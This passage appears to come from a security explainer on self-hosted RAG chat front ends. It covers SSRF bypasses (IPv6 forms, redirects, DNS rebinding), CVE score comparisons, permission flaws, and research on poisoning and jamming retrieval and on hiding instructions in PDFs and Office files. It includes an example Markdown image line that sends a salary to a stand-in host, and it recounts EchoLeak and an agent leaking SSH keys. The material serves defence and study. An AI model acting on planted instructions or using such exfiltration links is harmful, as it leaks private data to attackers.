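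On a rented cloud server, the attacker can also try to reach the metadata service. This service, usually at the internal address 169.254.169.254, gives programs on the machine its settings and temporary credentials for the cloud account. The credentials allow only what the operator has permitted that machine to do, so the "full cloud account takeover" described in the OSV entry would require broad permissions. Amazon's newer version of the service also requires a token that a simple page import can't request.

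The natural fix is to look up the address behind a host name and refuse the request if that address is private. Open WebUI added a function for this, but researchers kept finding ways around it.

One problem was that the function used a validation library to check whether an address in the newer IPv6 format was private, but with an option that the library did not support for IPv6. The library returned an error, which Python treats as "false" in a yes-or-no test, so every IPv6 address passed, including ordinary IPv4 addresses written in IPv6 form. The advisory in Corgea's *Open WebUI has a full SSRF Vulnerability in the RAG Web Search* credits a report from September 2024, and version 0.9.0 contains the fix. LibreChat had a similar flaw with IPv4 addresses in IPv6 form, recorded as CVE-2026-31943 in *LibreChat*, an online list of that program's flaws.

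Attackers could also use redirects to get past the address check. A public website can respond to a request by redirecting it to a different address. Open WebUI checked the address the user entered, then followed any redirect without checking where it led. GCVE's *GHSA-RH5X-H6PP-CJJ6* (2026) lists five places in the code with this flaw. The easiest to reach was the one that handled image links in ordinary chat messages. The advisory recommends turning off automatic redirects and checking each new address before following it. Version 0.9.5 fixed these cases, along with one in which the checking code and the fetching code interpreted the same web address differently, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-45400* (2026).

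An attacker can also change the address of a host name between the check and the fetch, which is called domain name system (DNS) rebinding. The server looks up the name's numerical address in DNS, and whoever owns the name controls the answer. They can give a public address for the check and an internal one a moment later, when the server connects. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54020* (2026) states that every user-reachable fetch relying on the check was affected before version 0.11.0.

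Open WebUI can also load pages with Playwright, a program that controls a real browser, which helps with pages that build their text using scripts. The browser made its own requests, so it needed the same protections again:

- Before 0.9.6, it followed redirects to internal addresses, according to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54018* (2026).
- From 0.9.6 until 0.11.0, the server checked the main page but not the other files that the page loaded, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-70479* (2026).
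- From 0.9.6 until 0.11.1, the browser looked up host names a second time, which allowed DNS rebinding, according to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-87996* (2026).

SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-87996* explains that, as of version 0.11.1, the server looks up the hostname once, downloads the content itself, checks any redirect and hands the result to the browser. Operators who can't update can switch back to the default page loader.

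The same release, from September 2026, closed two gaps that didn't depend on Playwright. Microsoft's Azure cloud uses 168.63.129.16 to communicate internally with its machines, but Python classifies that address as public, so Open WebUI let users fetch from it, according to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-87999* (2026). Redirects were also a risk again for operators who had enabled them, according to Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-88001* (2026). An operator who stopped updating at 0.6.37, believing the SSRF flaw fixed, was still exposed to most of these attacks.

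The best-known SSRF flaw in LibreChat, CVE-2025-69222, was in Actions, a feature that lets agents call outside services, rather than in document import. A user supplies a description of a service's address and functions, and the agent can then send requests to it. According to MITRE's *LibreChat is vulnerable to Server-Side Request Forgery due to missing restrictions* (2026), the default settings placed no limit on which services an agent could reach. These included LibreChat's own RAG API, the internal component that handles document retrieval, so the flaw still put documents at risk.

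The MITRE record lists 0.8.1-rc2 as both the vulnerable version and the fixed one. The fixed version is 0.8.2-rc2, according to the *SBA Security Advisory* from SBA Research, the Vienna institute whose researchers found the flaw. SBA Research also advises operators to list the permitted services, including protocol and port, in the setting `actions.allowedDomains`. Version 0.8.1-rc2 fixed an earlier SSRF flaw in Actions that allowed access to cloud metadata (MITRE, *CVE-2025-66201*).

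### Do these flaws deserve their scores?

| Flaw | Access the attacker needs | Score | Fixed in | Record |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2024-10513, AnythingLLM database | Manager | 7.2 | 1.2.2 | Tenable |
| CVE-2026-24478, AnythingLLM wiki import | Administrator, or an administrator's cooperation | 7.2 | 1.10.0 | Intruder |
| CVE-2026-5627, AnythingLLM agent flows | High privileges | 9.1 | 1.12.1 | OSV |
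| CVE-2026-48789, AnythingLLM on Windows | Account with few rights | 4.3 | 1.13.0 | OSV |
| CVE-2025-65958, Open WebUI page import | Any account | 8.5 | 0.6.37 | OSV |
| CVE-2025-69222, LibreChat Actions | Account with few rights | 9.1 | 0.8.2-rc2 | SBA Research |

The agent-flow flaw scores almost two points higher than the database flaw. This is hard to justify, because the agent-flow flaw exposes only `.json` files, while the database flaw exposes the application's whole database. The ratings differ only in the agent-flow flaw's "changed scope", without which it would also score 7.2. Shodan's *Vulnerability Details CVE-2026-5627* also lists an exploit prediction score of 0.001, an estimated 0.1% chance that someone will exploit the flaw within 30 days.

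A score of 7.2 for the database flaw seems fair. An attacker needs a manager's account, but managers are not supposed to have access to everyone's data, and stealing one manager's password is enough to exploit the flaw. The wiki flaw is less urgent for a firm whose only administrator also runs the server, since that person can already change any file on it. It matters more where a hosting company runs the server and the customer is an administrator only within AnythingLLM.

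Scores for nearly the same attack also vary. GCVE lists Open WebUI's redirect flaw at 8.5, while INCIBE's *CVE-2026-56399* (2026) lists a redirect flaw in the same page-import function at 5.0. INCIBE's June 2026 record lists only versions before 0.6.27 as vulnerable, although the advisory GCVE lists had shown a month earlier that redirects still worked in 0.9.4. DNS rebinding scores 6.3 in Open WebUI's general fetching code and 7.7 in its Playwright loader, because the first record rates the attack as difficult and the second rates it as easy, though both attacks require an account and control of a domain's DNS.

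Open WebUI's upload flaws have similarly inconsistent severity scores. The prompt-attachment flaw scores 7.3 and requires no privileges, while the audio-upload flaw scores 8.1 even though the attacker needs an account. Both let the attacker write files outside the upload folder, but the audio flaw has the higher harm rating. The "no privileges" rating is reasonable for the attachment flaw because the same versions also had the pending-user flaw. KoreLogic reported the attachment flaw in March 2024, but its entry in GitHub's advisory database dates from May 2026, according to OSV's *GHSA-9pgh-j74g-qj6m* (2026).

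For most teams, the SSRF flaws deserve attention before the higher-scoring flaw in agent flows, because any employee with an account can exploit them. The danger is greatest on a cloud server whose credentials give wide access. SSRF gives the sole user of a home server almost nothing, since they can already reach the other machines on the network directly. Parser flaws are still a concern there, because the owner may upload a file that a stranger wrote.

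## How can a retrieved document mislead the model?

A file that doesn't harm the server during extraction can still mislead the model later, when the front end adds one of the file's chunks to the model's input. Whoever wrote the chunk can influence an answer that someone else receives, but only if the search returns the chunk and the model acts on it.

### Getting into the model's input

The front end compares the question's embedding, q, with the embedding c of every stored chunk. With cosine similarity, each chunk's score is:

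```
similarity(q, c) = (q · c) / (|q| × |c|)
```

The dot product at the top of the fraction comes from multiplying the two lists of numbers pair by pair and adding the results. For the vectors (3, 4) and (4, 3), the dot product is 24 and each magnitude is 5, so the similarity is 24/25, or 0.96. Real embeddings have hundreds or thousands of numbers. The front end ranks the chunks by score and passes the top k to the model. The number k is a setting, and most of the experiments described below use a value between 3 and 10.

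Suppose a hotel in Graz sends the invented engineering firm a brochure, and the office manager uploads it. One paragraph states that the firm now refunds up to 250 euros a night. When an employee asks how much she can claim for a hotel in Graz, with k set to 3, the scores might be:

| Chunk | Similarity | Sent to the model |
|---|---|---|
| Travel policy, hotel limits | 0.84 | Yes |
| Hotel brochure, planted paragraph | 0.79 | Yes |
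| Graz office guide, directions | 0.66 | Yes |
| Travel policy, train fares | 0.58 | No |
| Staff handbook, parental leave | 0.21 | No |

Without the brochure, the chunk about train fares would have ranked third with a score of 0.58. The planted paragraph only had to beat that score, not outrank the genuine policy. The score to beat is lowest for subjects on which the firm has few documents.

*Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier* (Chang, Bao and colleagues, 2026) measured this threshold in public collections of 26,000 to 8.8 million documents. In MS MARCO, a collection of web pages, the fifth-best genuine document scored 0.75 on average where the paper's attack succeeded and 0.82 where it failed. Collection size made no visible difference.

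One study found that a plain malicious instruction never reached the top five search results in any of the 11 document collections tested, because it doesn't resemble anything a user would ask. The simplest way for an attacker to get around this is to start the planted text with the question they expect a user to ask. In a collection of debating arguments, that worked only about 20% of the time.

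Chang and colleagues did better by searching for a short string of tokens that moves the whole text's embedding closer to the question's. Their program generates 5,000 random strings, keeps the best-scoring fifth, makes the tokens in those strings more likely in the next batch, and repeats this 30 times. With OpenAI's embedding service, the search cost $0.21 per question. In seven of the collections, strings of five to ten tokens were enough to get the planted text into the top five almost every time.

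This method depends on knowing the embedding model or guessing it well. A string optimised for one small Qwen model worked on an OpenAI model only 10% of the time. Self-hosted front ends offer limited protection because anyone can look up the default embedding model in an open-source project's code and, if the model is public, optimise a string for it on their own computer.

### What repeated questions do to the odds

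Let r be the probability that the search returns the planted text, and a the probability that the model acts on the text once it is returned. The attack succeeds on a single question with probability r × a. If r is 80% and a is 50%, the probability of success is 40%.

If n people ask and each attempt independently succeeds with probability ra, the probability of at least one success is 1 − (1 − ra)^n. When ra is 0.4, the probability over five questions is 1 − 0.6^5, or 92%. Even an attack that works 1% of the time has an 87% chance of succeeding at least once in 200 questions.

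Assuming that the questions are independent favors the attacker, because repeating a question against the same collection returns the same chunks and gives the planted text no new chance to appear. Suppose instead that the 80% is the chance that the attacker has judged the collection and the embedding model well enough for the text to appear at all. The total chance over five questions is then 0.8 × (1 − 0.5^5), or 78%, and no number of questions can raise it above 80%. Because questions differ in wording, most real cases fall somewhere between the two calculations.

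### False answers

The Graz brochure contains a false claim but no command, which researchers call knowledge poisoning. If it contained an instruction to the model instead, the attack would be indirect prompt injection. In jamming, the planted text makes the model refuse to answer or give a useless answer. A supplier might use jamming to keep the model from reporting bad reviews of the supplier in the firm's files.

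Research on false answers grew quickly after Zou, Geng and colleagues (2024) published *PoisonedRAG*. For each of 100 factual questions, they had GPT-4 write five passages of about 30 words supporting a wrong answer, and put the question in front of each passage. They added these to a collection of 2.68 million passages from Wikipedia. The attacker knew the questions but had no access to the search system or the model that answered. When GPT-4 answered the questions, it gave the planted wrong answer 97% of the time.

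Two control tests show why the planted text needs both the question and a misleading passage. Texts that only repeated the question always appeared in the search results but produced the wrong answer in 3% of cases. Passages without the question produced the wrong answer in 69% of cases, and the search returned only about half of them.

The 97% figure is weak evidence of what an attacker could do by planting a single document. The system retrieved five passages and the attacker had planted five, so nearly everything retrieved was planted and the model rarely saw the right answer. *Practical Poisoning Attacks against Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2025) also objects that the method works only when the planted passages outnumber those containing the right answer. The paper introduces CorruptRAG, an attack that needs only one passage, which describes the right answer as outdated and the wrong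 one as the latest information.

Zhurekbay, Liu and Li (2026), in *DenialRAG*, tested five such single-passage attacks on eight models. The newest OpenAI model in their comparison was GPT-5.5, though OpenAI has since released newer ones. On GPT-5.5, CorruptRAG succeeded on 76% of the questions in the Wikipedia-based set that Zou and colleagues used, while a single PoisonedRAG passage, which simply asserts the wrong answer, succeeded on 46%.

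In the researchers' own attack, the planted passage includes the right answer and an explanation of why it is supposedly wrong. For a television season with 23 episodes, the passage gave the number as 24 and said the figure of 23 came from summaries that had counted a two-part finale as one episode. The attack worked on 89% of the questions with Mistral 7B, a small model, but on only 44% with GPT-5.5. When the researchers removed the denial and left only the false claim, the success rate fell by an average of 17 percentage points.

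*Ranking Is Not Deciding* (2026) observes that false corrections are hard to filter out because genuine ones look the same. The firm's real travel policy, for example, tells staff to disregard the limits in earlier editions. A model that distrusted every such sentence would keep quoting the old limit after a real change. The system also needs to know where each passage came from, because it can't tell which one to believe from the wording alone.

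The system's design also makes a large difference. Korn (2026), in *Architecture Matters*, planted one CorruptRAG passage per question among 2.68 million and used GPT-5-mini in every test. An ordinary design, which retrieves ten passages and calls the model once, gave the attacker's answer to 81.9% of the questions it otherwise got right. A "recursive language model", which uses code to inspect and compare a much larger set of passages on the topic, did so for 24.4%. Without an attack, both answered about 92% of the questions correctly.

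Korn kept only questions for which the normal search found good evidence, so the models usually had other evidence to compare with the planted text. They would have less in a firm with only one document on the subject, which would make the attack easier.

Korn also tested a design in which ten copies of the model each read one passage and then debate. It often appeared to detect contradictions but could not reliably resolve them, and it failed to answer 41.4% of questions even when nobody had planted anything. Korn cautions that differences from the original design may partly explain these results.

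Many published success rates are probably too high, because researchers often count any answer that contains the planted string. An answer such as "one source says 24 episodes, but this appears to be wrong" would count as a success for the attacker. Dahal and Xiong (2026), in *Prevented is Not Protected*, compared this method with checking whether the response endorsed the planted answer, using Llama 3 8B and 100 questions with one planted passage. The planted answer appeared in 60 responses, but a second model used as a judge classified only 35 as endorsing it and 9 as uncertain. Zhurekbay and colleagues counted strings, so their figures are probably somewhat high too. The effect was smaller in the test by Zou and colleagues, where checking by hand lowered the attack's success rate against GPT-4 from 97% to 92%.

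### Chunking, rewording and reranking

Most early experiments assumed that the system stores the planted text whole and that the user types exactly the question the attacker expected. A real front end can split the planted passage between chunks, leaving the question in one and the false claim in another.

In *Confundo*, Hu, Jiang and colleagues (2026) tested attacks using questions about Harry Potter, with documents split into 128-token chunks and three chunks retrieved per question. The best of the older attacks reached a 54% success rate with Llama 3 8B. When the researchers reworded the questions, the older attacks lost a further 40 to 50% of their success.

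An operator who tested only those older attacks would be too confident. Hu and colleagues also trained a small model to write planted passages, rewarding passages that still worked after a random cut and with several wordings of the question. Its passages averaged 31 words and succeeded 88% of the time, and rewording the questions lowered their success rate by only 7%. They succeeded 86% to 92% of the time against a range of other models, including Gemini 2.5 Pro.

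Studies disagree about how much reranking by a second model helps against attacks. *Reranker Helps, but Not Enough* describes it as a strong obstacle to earlier attacks, though a new attack gets past it with very small changes to the text. Hu and colleagues saw little effect. This may be because they appear to have only reordered chunks that the model would have received anyway, whereas the other study's reranker could leave chunks out.

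| Test | Planted texts per question | Collection | What the attacker knows | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Zou and colleagues | 5 | 2.68 million Wikipedia passages | The question | 97% (GPT-4) |
| Zhurekbay and colleagues | 1 | The same Wikipedia-based question set | The question and the right answer | 38% to 76%, depending on the attack (GPT-5.5) |
| Korn | 1 | 2.68 million Wikipedia passages | The question and the right answer | 24.4% to 81.9%, depending on the system's design (GPT-5-mini) |
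| Hu and colleagues | 1 | Harry Potter text in 128-token chunks | The question, perhaps in other words | 54% for the best older attack, 88% for the new one (Llama 3 8B) |

The example of the supplier's brochure is closest to the single-text tests. Suppliers can often guess what a customer's staff will ask, but they rarely know the exact wording or what else is in the collection. A careful attacker's realistic success rate is therefore well below 97%, but still high enough that a firm shouldn't rely on the model to recognise a false passage.

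### Instructions hidden in documents

Chang and colleagues also measured what happens after a planted instruction reaches the model. They used a text that told the model to answer "Yes" to everything. A single such text in the collection made most of the 11 open models they tried answer "Yes" to nearly all questions, even when the question was about a series of books. Models trained to follow instructions were generally more vulnerable, and larger models were no safer.

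Commercial models released since then show some improvement. One of the five attacks in the comparison by Zhurekbay and colleagues is closer to a direct instruction than to a false fact. It succeeded 91% to 99% of the time on GPT-5.2, depending on the set of questions, and 53% to 57% on GPT-5.5.

*Semantic Chameleon* (2026) reports attack success rates of 46.7% for GPT-5.3, 60% for Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 93.3% for Llama 4. These rates depend on what counts as success. Claude often acknowledged the planted material, but only 6.7% of its answers broke the safety rules by passing on something harmful. All the percentages are multiples of one fifteenth, which suggests about 15 trials per model. If so, the difference between GPT-5.3 and Claude would be only two answers.

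That attack plants two documents and fails unless the search returns both. In a collection of computer-security discussions, the search returned both 44.4% of the time, and the full attack succeeded only 11.1% of the time. An attack can therefore succeed often when tested on the model alone but rarely when carried out in full.

The damage also depends on what the model can do. In the engineering firm, a model without tools can only write a misleading answer. Chang and colleagues tested a team of AI agents that could read email and run code. They planted one email among many genuine ones on the same subject, and the user asked for a summary of a routine procedure. In more than 80% of trials, GPT-4o ran a script that sent the attacker the user's SSH keys, which can be used to log in to other machines.

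### Refusals and useless answers

In *Machine Against the RAG* (2024), Shafran, Schuster and Shmatikov studied jamming with a single "blocker" document. The document starts with the expected question, so that the search finds it, and continues with about 50 tokens chosen to make the model refuse to answer. The attacker starts with a row of exclamation marks in place of these tokens and swaps one at a time. The attacker sends the question to the system to test each version, and keeps the one that brings the answer closest to a refusal such as "I don't know".

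Blocker documents, each written to stop the model from answering a particular question, prevented 28% to 73% of the answers that six small and medium-sized models would otherwise have given. The test collections held 2.6 million and 8.8 million documents, and the system retrieved five documents for each question. The search returned a blocker for its target question more than 97% of the time and never for any other question, so colleagues asking other questions would notice nothing wrong.

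The attacker in this test needs unusual access, because they have to edit their own document repeatedly and put questions to the system. One blocker takes about 5,000 questions, with 32 new candidates a round and 160 rounds on average. An employee with an account could do that if nobody watched the logs, but not an outsider who only supplies a document, such as a hotel sending a brochure. Preparing the blocker on a different model doesn't help much, because at most 19% of the blockers worked when the researchers moved them between the six models.

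A retrieved document can also block an answer with a plain instruction to ignore the other documents and reply "I don't know". This requires no optimisation, and it stopped up to 90% of answers on some of the models. Most of these models date from 2023 and 2024. In a small test with ten questions per model, blocking documents optimised directly against each model stopped one answer from GPT-4o and three from GPT-4o mini.

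Jamming is harder to notice than a false answer. Someone can check "250 euros" against the policy, but "the documents do not contain this information" looks like an ordinary search failure. Shafran and colleagues also found that models with higher scores on an existing safety benchmark tended to be more vulnerable, probably because they refuse more readily.

An attacker can also plant text to make the model answer with nonsense. Hu and colleagues used this method to raise Llama 3 8B's share of made-up or irrelevant answers from 2% to 95%. In one example, a user asked how to fold a quilt and received an answer unrelated to quilts.

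### Text that people cannot see

The office manager might have noticed the paragraph about 250 euros if she had read the brochure before uploading it. But attackers can hide text from a person and still leave it for a text extractor to find. A PDF stores text with instructions for drawing it, including its position, font and layer, and whether to paint the letters at all. A PDF viewer follows those instructions, but an extractor may collect the characters and ignore the rest.

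According to *PhantomLint* (2025), an author can hide text in a PDF by putting it on a layer that is switched off, placing it outside the visible part of the page, drawing it in a mode that paints nothing, or using a font in which every character is blank. *CrackedPDFs* (2026) describes fonts that show the reader one letter while the file stores another. It also notes that comments in a web page's code don't appear on the displayed page but can stay in the text that the model receives. *Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (2026), which covers web content, lists zero-width characters as another way to hide text.

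Extractors can't discard all invisible text. Scanned documents often have a hidden layer of recognised text behind the picture of the page that makes them searchable. If an extractor dropped that layer, the text of the firm's scanned contracts would be missing from its collection.

*The Hidden Threat in Plain Text* (Castagnaro, Salviati and colleagues, 2025) tested the programs that load files into RAG systems. The researchers tried 19 hiding techniques in Word, HTML and PDF files against five popular loaders, and the attacks succeeded in 74.4% of 357 scenarios. They also attacked six complete systems, including Google's NotebookLM and OpenAI's Assistants, and again reported high success rates.

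The text extracted from an Office file can differ from what a reader sees. Li (2026), in *When File Ingestion Misleads Language Models*, examined ten extractors for Word, Excel and PowerPoint files. Li found 19 places in these formats where at least one extractor picked up text that a reader would not see, such as passages marked as hidden in Word and hidden rows, columns or sheets in Excel. Li also found 12 places where at least one extractor dropped text that a reader would see.

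Some of Li's attacks work without hiding anything. An Excel cell can contain 1,000,000 but have a number format that displays it in thousands, so a manager sees $1,000 and approves the budget. An extractor that ignores the format gives the model the full million. In another attack, moving text boxes slightly on a slide changes the order in which the model reads them, but the slide looks the same to a person. *What Users See Is Not What Models Read* (2026) describes comparable mismatches in PDFs. A filter for suspicious instructions won't catch these files because they contain none.

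Li tried five such attacks on commercial products such as ChatGPT, Claude and Microsoft 365 Copilot. At least one attack worked on each of the four chat assistants and four coding agents tested. The number format alone misled all four assistants and three of the agents in at least nine of ten trials. An operator of a self-hosted front end can test its extractor by uploading a spreadsheet with a hidden row and a number shown in thousands, then asking about both.

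Job applicants already hide text in CVs to influence automated screening. Hidden text causes the most trouble when the person who checks a file is not the one who relies on the answer. This is normal in a shared document collection, where an office manager might check a brochure once, and months later an employee who has never seen it asks a question that the model answers from it.

### How private text can leave through a picture

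Planted text can change what the user reads or what the model does with its tools. It can also leak information through the chat page, even if the model has no tools.

Models format their answers in Markdown, a simple text notation. A Markdown image consists of a short label and a web address, which the browser requests automatically when it displays the image. The address can carry extra text after a question mark, and the server can record everything it receives.

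Suppose the brochure tells the model to end each answer with a picture and to copy any salary it has seen into the picture's address. An employee in the accounts department asks a question, and the search returns a chunk of the salary file along with the brochure. The model might then add this line to its answer:

```
![map](https://pictures.example/map.png?note=salary-61000)
```

The employee sees a map or a broken-image symbol, and the hotel's server log contains the salary. Checking permissions before the search does not prevent this, because the employee is allowed to read the salary file. Removing scripts from the page doesn't help either, because the line contains only an image. The attacker can obtain anything in the model's input this way, including the system prompt and earlier messages in the chat. A link can send the same data, but only if the user clicks it.

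Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a company's email and files, had a flaw of this kind, recorded as CVE-2025-32711. *EchoLeak* (2025) sets out the attack, which the security researchers at Aim Labs had described:

1. The attacker, who has no access to the company's systems, sends an employee an email containing instructions for the model.
2. The employee later asks Copilot for sensitive information, and Copilot processes the email along with other material.
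3. Copilot's answer includes an image whose address contains the sensitive information.
4. The employee's browser requests the image and delivers the information to the attacker.

The employee doesn't have to open the email or click on anything. The attack got past Copilot's classifier for detecting prompt injection, its filter for removing external links from answers, and its content security policy, which limits the sites the page can load material from.

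A self-hosted front end is exposed to the same attack if its page loads images from any website. It is unclear which of Open WebUI, LibreChat, AnythingLLM and Dify do so by default, so operators need to test the version they have installed. They can put a picture on a web server whose log they can read, ask the model to reply with a Markdown image link to it, and check the log for a request.

The log also shows whether the user's browser or the front end's server requested the picture. If the server requested it, the user's network address stays hidden, but any private text in the link still reaches the attacker.

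## Who can read and change what in a shared workspace?

In the hypothetical engineering firm, only the accounts department should read the salary file. The office manager can set that rule quickly, but the front end has to apply it to every copy of the file's text and every request that can reach a copy.

| What the server stores | Requests that can reach it | Who should get it |
|---|---|---|
| The original file | Download, preview, deletion | People with rights to the file |
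| Its chunks and embeddings | A search, or a chat that starts one | People who may read the file at that moment |
| Chats that quote it | Opening, sharing or streaming a chat, or having it read aloud | The chat's owner and anyone they share it with |
| A search index of all chats | The search box | Each user, for their own chats only |
| Links from agents, folders and collections | Editing the agent, folder or collection | People with rights to both the file and the thing that uses it |

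Developers have to call the permission check in each function that handles one of these requests, and in Open WebUI they missed several. A chat request can point to documents in five ways, and Corgea's *Unauthorized File and Knowledge Base Content Access via RAG Vector Search* explains that only two of them led to a check. The server checked requests for a whole file but not the default kind, which searches the file for relevant chunks. A designer who wasn't allowed to open the salary file could therefore still get the server to pass its most relevant passages to the model.

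This flaw, CVE-2026-44560, has a severity score of 6.5. The advisory describes all versions with document retrieval as probably affected and does not list a fixed version. Closely related flaws were fixed in releases from 0.9.5 to 0.11.0.

To exploit it, an attacker needs an account and the file's identifier. Open WebUI's identifiers contain 122 random bits, so trying them all at a billion guesses a second would take more than 10^20 years. Finding an identifier is much easier than guessing one. *PYSEC-2026-2699* (Orr, 2026) lists several places where the identifiers of document collections appear, including page addresses, browser histories and the source references in shared chats. A shared model's details also include the identifiers of its collections, even for users who can't open them, so having an identifier doesn't prove that a user has permission to see the record.

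### Filtering before or after the search

Suppose the firm keeps the chunks of two teams, accounts and design, in one vector database. A designer asks what a week's delay in Graz would cost. With k set to 4, the front end wants the four best chunks, and the ranking looks like this:

| Rank | Chunk | Team | Similarity |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Salary file, day rates | Accounts | 0.86 |
| 2 | Graz budget, staff costs | Accounts | 0.83 |
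| 3 | Graz schedule, delays | Design | 0.80 |
| 4 | Graz invoices, summary | Accounts | 0.77 |
| 5 | Builder's contract, penalties | Design | 0.71 |
| 6 | Site meeting, minutes | Design | 0.68 |
| 7 | Overtime rules | Accounts | 0.66 |
| 8 | List of revised drawings | Design | 0.60 |

If the front end filters after the search, it takes the chunks ranked 1 to 4, removes the three accounts chunks and gives the model only the schedule. If it filters before the search, it searches only the design chunks and gives the model those ranked 3, 5, 6 and 8 overall.

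A front end that filters chunks by permission after the search can compensate by fetching more of them. If a user may read a share p of all chunks, and permission is unrelated to relevance, the front end has to fetch about k/p chunks to end up with k on average. To end up with four, it would have to fetch eight for the designer, who can read half the collection, and 200 for a temporary worker who can read 2% of it. In practice, permission is related to relevance because firms restrict documents by subject. A question about pay might return only restricted accounts chunks, however many the front end fetches.

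Filtering by permission before or after retrieval can keep restricted text away from the model, but filtering afterwards leaves more room for mistakes. The restricted chunks have already left the database, so if the front end sends them to an outside reranking service before filtering them, that service could receive a confidential salary file. Filtering afterwards can also shorten the list of results, and a designer who sees one source instead of her usual four can guess that documents she isn't allowed to read contain closer matches.

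Filtering before the search requires either a label on each chunk that records who may read it or a separate collection for each group of readers. It can also make the search miss relevant chunks. Many vector databases search by following links between similar embeddings rather than comparing the question with every chunk, and a strict filter can leave too few permitted chunks along those links.

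Open WebUI separates documents into collections, one for each file and one for each "knowledge base" (a group of documents). The server is supposed to check that the user may read a collection before searching it, and to search only that collection. Because this filters whole collections before the search, individual chunks don't need labels, but a single route that lacks the check can let users search collections they aren't allowed to read.

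### When someone loses access

Suppose the designer helps the accounts department for a month, and the office manager then removes her from its group. If the front end copied the group's member list into each chunk's label during ingestion, searches can still return those chunks to her until something rewrites the labels. Labels that name only the group avoid this, provided the server checks the group's membership at each search.

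Open WebUI did this on one route and not on another. When a user tried to open a knowledge base, the server looked up the current group memberships and refused anyone without access. But the search functions gave the same person the chunks. Orr traced this to a function that decided what to check from the first letters of the collection's name:

```
Name begins with "user-memory-":  is this the user's own memory?
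Name begins with "file-":         may the user read this file?
Any other name:                   no check
```

A knowledge base's name is its bare identifier, so it fell into the last group. A function that rejected every unrecognised name would have broken the search for knowledge bases, and the developers would have noticed at once.

The flaw, CVE-2026-45398, also let people change documents. Five of the functions for adding content didn't check the destination, so an attacker could plant text in someone else's knowledge base. The function for importing a web page replaced the whole collection by default, so one request could destroy it. The most likely attacker is a former project member, because they already know the collection's identifier. The flaw has a severity score of 7.5. According to Tenable's *Open WebUI Multiple Vulnerabilities*, Tenable reported the flaw on March 26, 2026,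 and Open WebUI published its advisory on May 10. Version 0.9.5 fixes the flaw.

Credentials can also keep working after a user's access is revoked. OSV's *CVE-2026-32717* describes how AnythingLLM 1.11.1 and earlier blocked suspended users who used the normal login but still accepted their browser extension keys. With such a key, a suspended user could keep uploading documents and reading workspace details.

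A related flaw affected AnythingLLM installations that began in single-user mode and later switched to multi-user mode. A phone connected before the switch held a token with no user attached. According to Tenable's *CVE-2026-47713* (2026), the server still accepted that token, skipped the filter because there was no user to check, and returned other people's workspaces and chats. Version 1.13.0 fixes this. On older versions, an operator who makes the same switch should then disconnect and reconnect every phone.

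Changing permissions cannot undo what someone has already read. If a designer had access to a salary file for a month, their chats from that month still contain whatever the model quoted from it.

### Routes that nobody checked

The missing checks are often on side routes, while the main page works correctly. LibreChat indexes chats with a separate search engine, Meilisearch. LibreChat's developers left a route for testing that engine open to outsiders, and it returned any user's chats, according to OSV's *CVE-2025-54868* (2025). The flaw is one of the worst of this kind because its score of 7.5 assumes an attacker with no account, and the record doesn't mention any need for an identifier. It was present from version 0.0.6 until version 0.7.7 removed it.

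The next full release, 0.7.8, had a similar problem in its sharing feature. Any logged-in user who knew a conversation's identifier could read the conversation, even if its owner had not shared it. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-6088 Detail* (2025), these identifiers appear in browser histories, server logs and screenshots. Version 0.7.9-rc1 fixes the flaw.

The same omission later occurred in LibreChat's streaming of answers. In versions 0.8.2-rc2 and 0.8.2-rc3, a user who had a stream's identifier could follow someone else's chat live, including the model's tool calls. CVELogic lists this as CVE-2026-31950, with a score of 5.3 and a fix in 0.8.2.

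AnythingLLM can read answers aloud, but before version 1.12.1 its text-to-speech function checked only that the user belonged to the workspace. OSV's *CVE-2026-42456* (2026) explains that one member could therefore listen to the model's private replies to another. Workspace members can usually read the shared documents, but not everything their colleagues have asked about them.

Some routes skip the permission checks on models. Before Open WebUI 0.9.0, the main chat function checked whether a user had access to a model, but a second function, which sent requests to OpenAI-style providers, checked only that the user was logged in. According to the security company Rapid7, this flaw (CVE-2026-44556) let any user reach any model on the installation by naming it. A firm that reserved an expensive model for a few people would have paid for any use of it by others.

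AnythingLLM 1.8.5 let anyone list its workspaces without logging in, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-63390 Detail* (2025). The list included each workspace's name, model, search settings and system prompt, but not its documents. The record lists no fixed version. Liu and colleagues, who discovered the flaw, give its severity score as 5.3 and write that they went to the CVE programme only after the affected projects had failed to respond adequately. In their survey, however, only a minority of the AnythingLLM servers they could reach returned the list. Many of those servers may have had no password because it is optional, so setting one is a sensible precaution on any version.

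A check can also fail to protect a file because the program carries on even when the check rejects the request. From version 1.11.1 until 1.14.1, AnythingLLM checked who owned an uploaded file before adding it to a workspace, but its cleanup code then deleted the file whatever the result. According to OffSeq's *CVE-2026-55611*, the server reported "File not found" and deleted the file anyway. The attacker had to be a manager or administrator, but could delete files in workspaces they didn't belong to. AnythingLLM numbers these files with ordinary integers, so the attacker could guess the numbers by counting upwards.

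### Borrowed permissions

Users rarely share files one at a time. They put a file into a knowledge base or attach it to a model, and everyone with access to that container can then use the file. Open WebUI's rule for this was roughly:

```
A user may read a file if
    the user owns it, or
    it is in a container that the user may read
```

The rule is safe only if people must have access to a file before they can add it to a container. Otherwise, an attacker can create an empty container, add another user's file by its identifier, and gain access to it because they own the container.

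Open WebUI had this flaw in several kinds of container. OSV's *GHSA-r472-mw7m-967f* (2026) covers folders and knowledge bases. An attacker could add someone else's file to a folder and ask about it in a chat there. The page removed unreadable files from the folder only when it next listed the user's folders, after the model had already answered. Adding the file to a knowledge base was worse, because the attacker could then overwrite the file.

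In Open WebUI versions before 0.9.6, an attacker could also open or delete another user's file by attaching it to a chat message and sharing the chat with themselves, according to Positive Technologies' *Unknown · Open-Webui · CVE-2026-54010*. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-54012* reports that anyone allowed to create a saved model could use one to do the same.

Version 0.9.6 added a check that a model's owner could read the files attached to it, but this still wasn't enough. GitLab's *CVE-2026-59212* (2026) explains that the functions for changing and deleting files treated the attachment as evidence of write access. A user who could only read a file could therefore attach it to their own model and then delete it. The check has to cover every right that a container, such as a model, grants over its files. If owning the model brings write access to its files, attaching a file must require write access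 too. Lutra Security's *CVE-2026-59212* (2026) lists a severity score of 5.4 and a fix in version 0.10.0.

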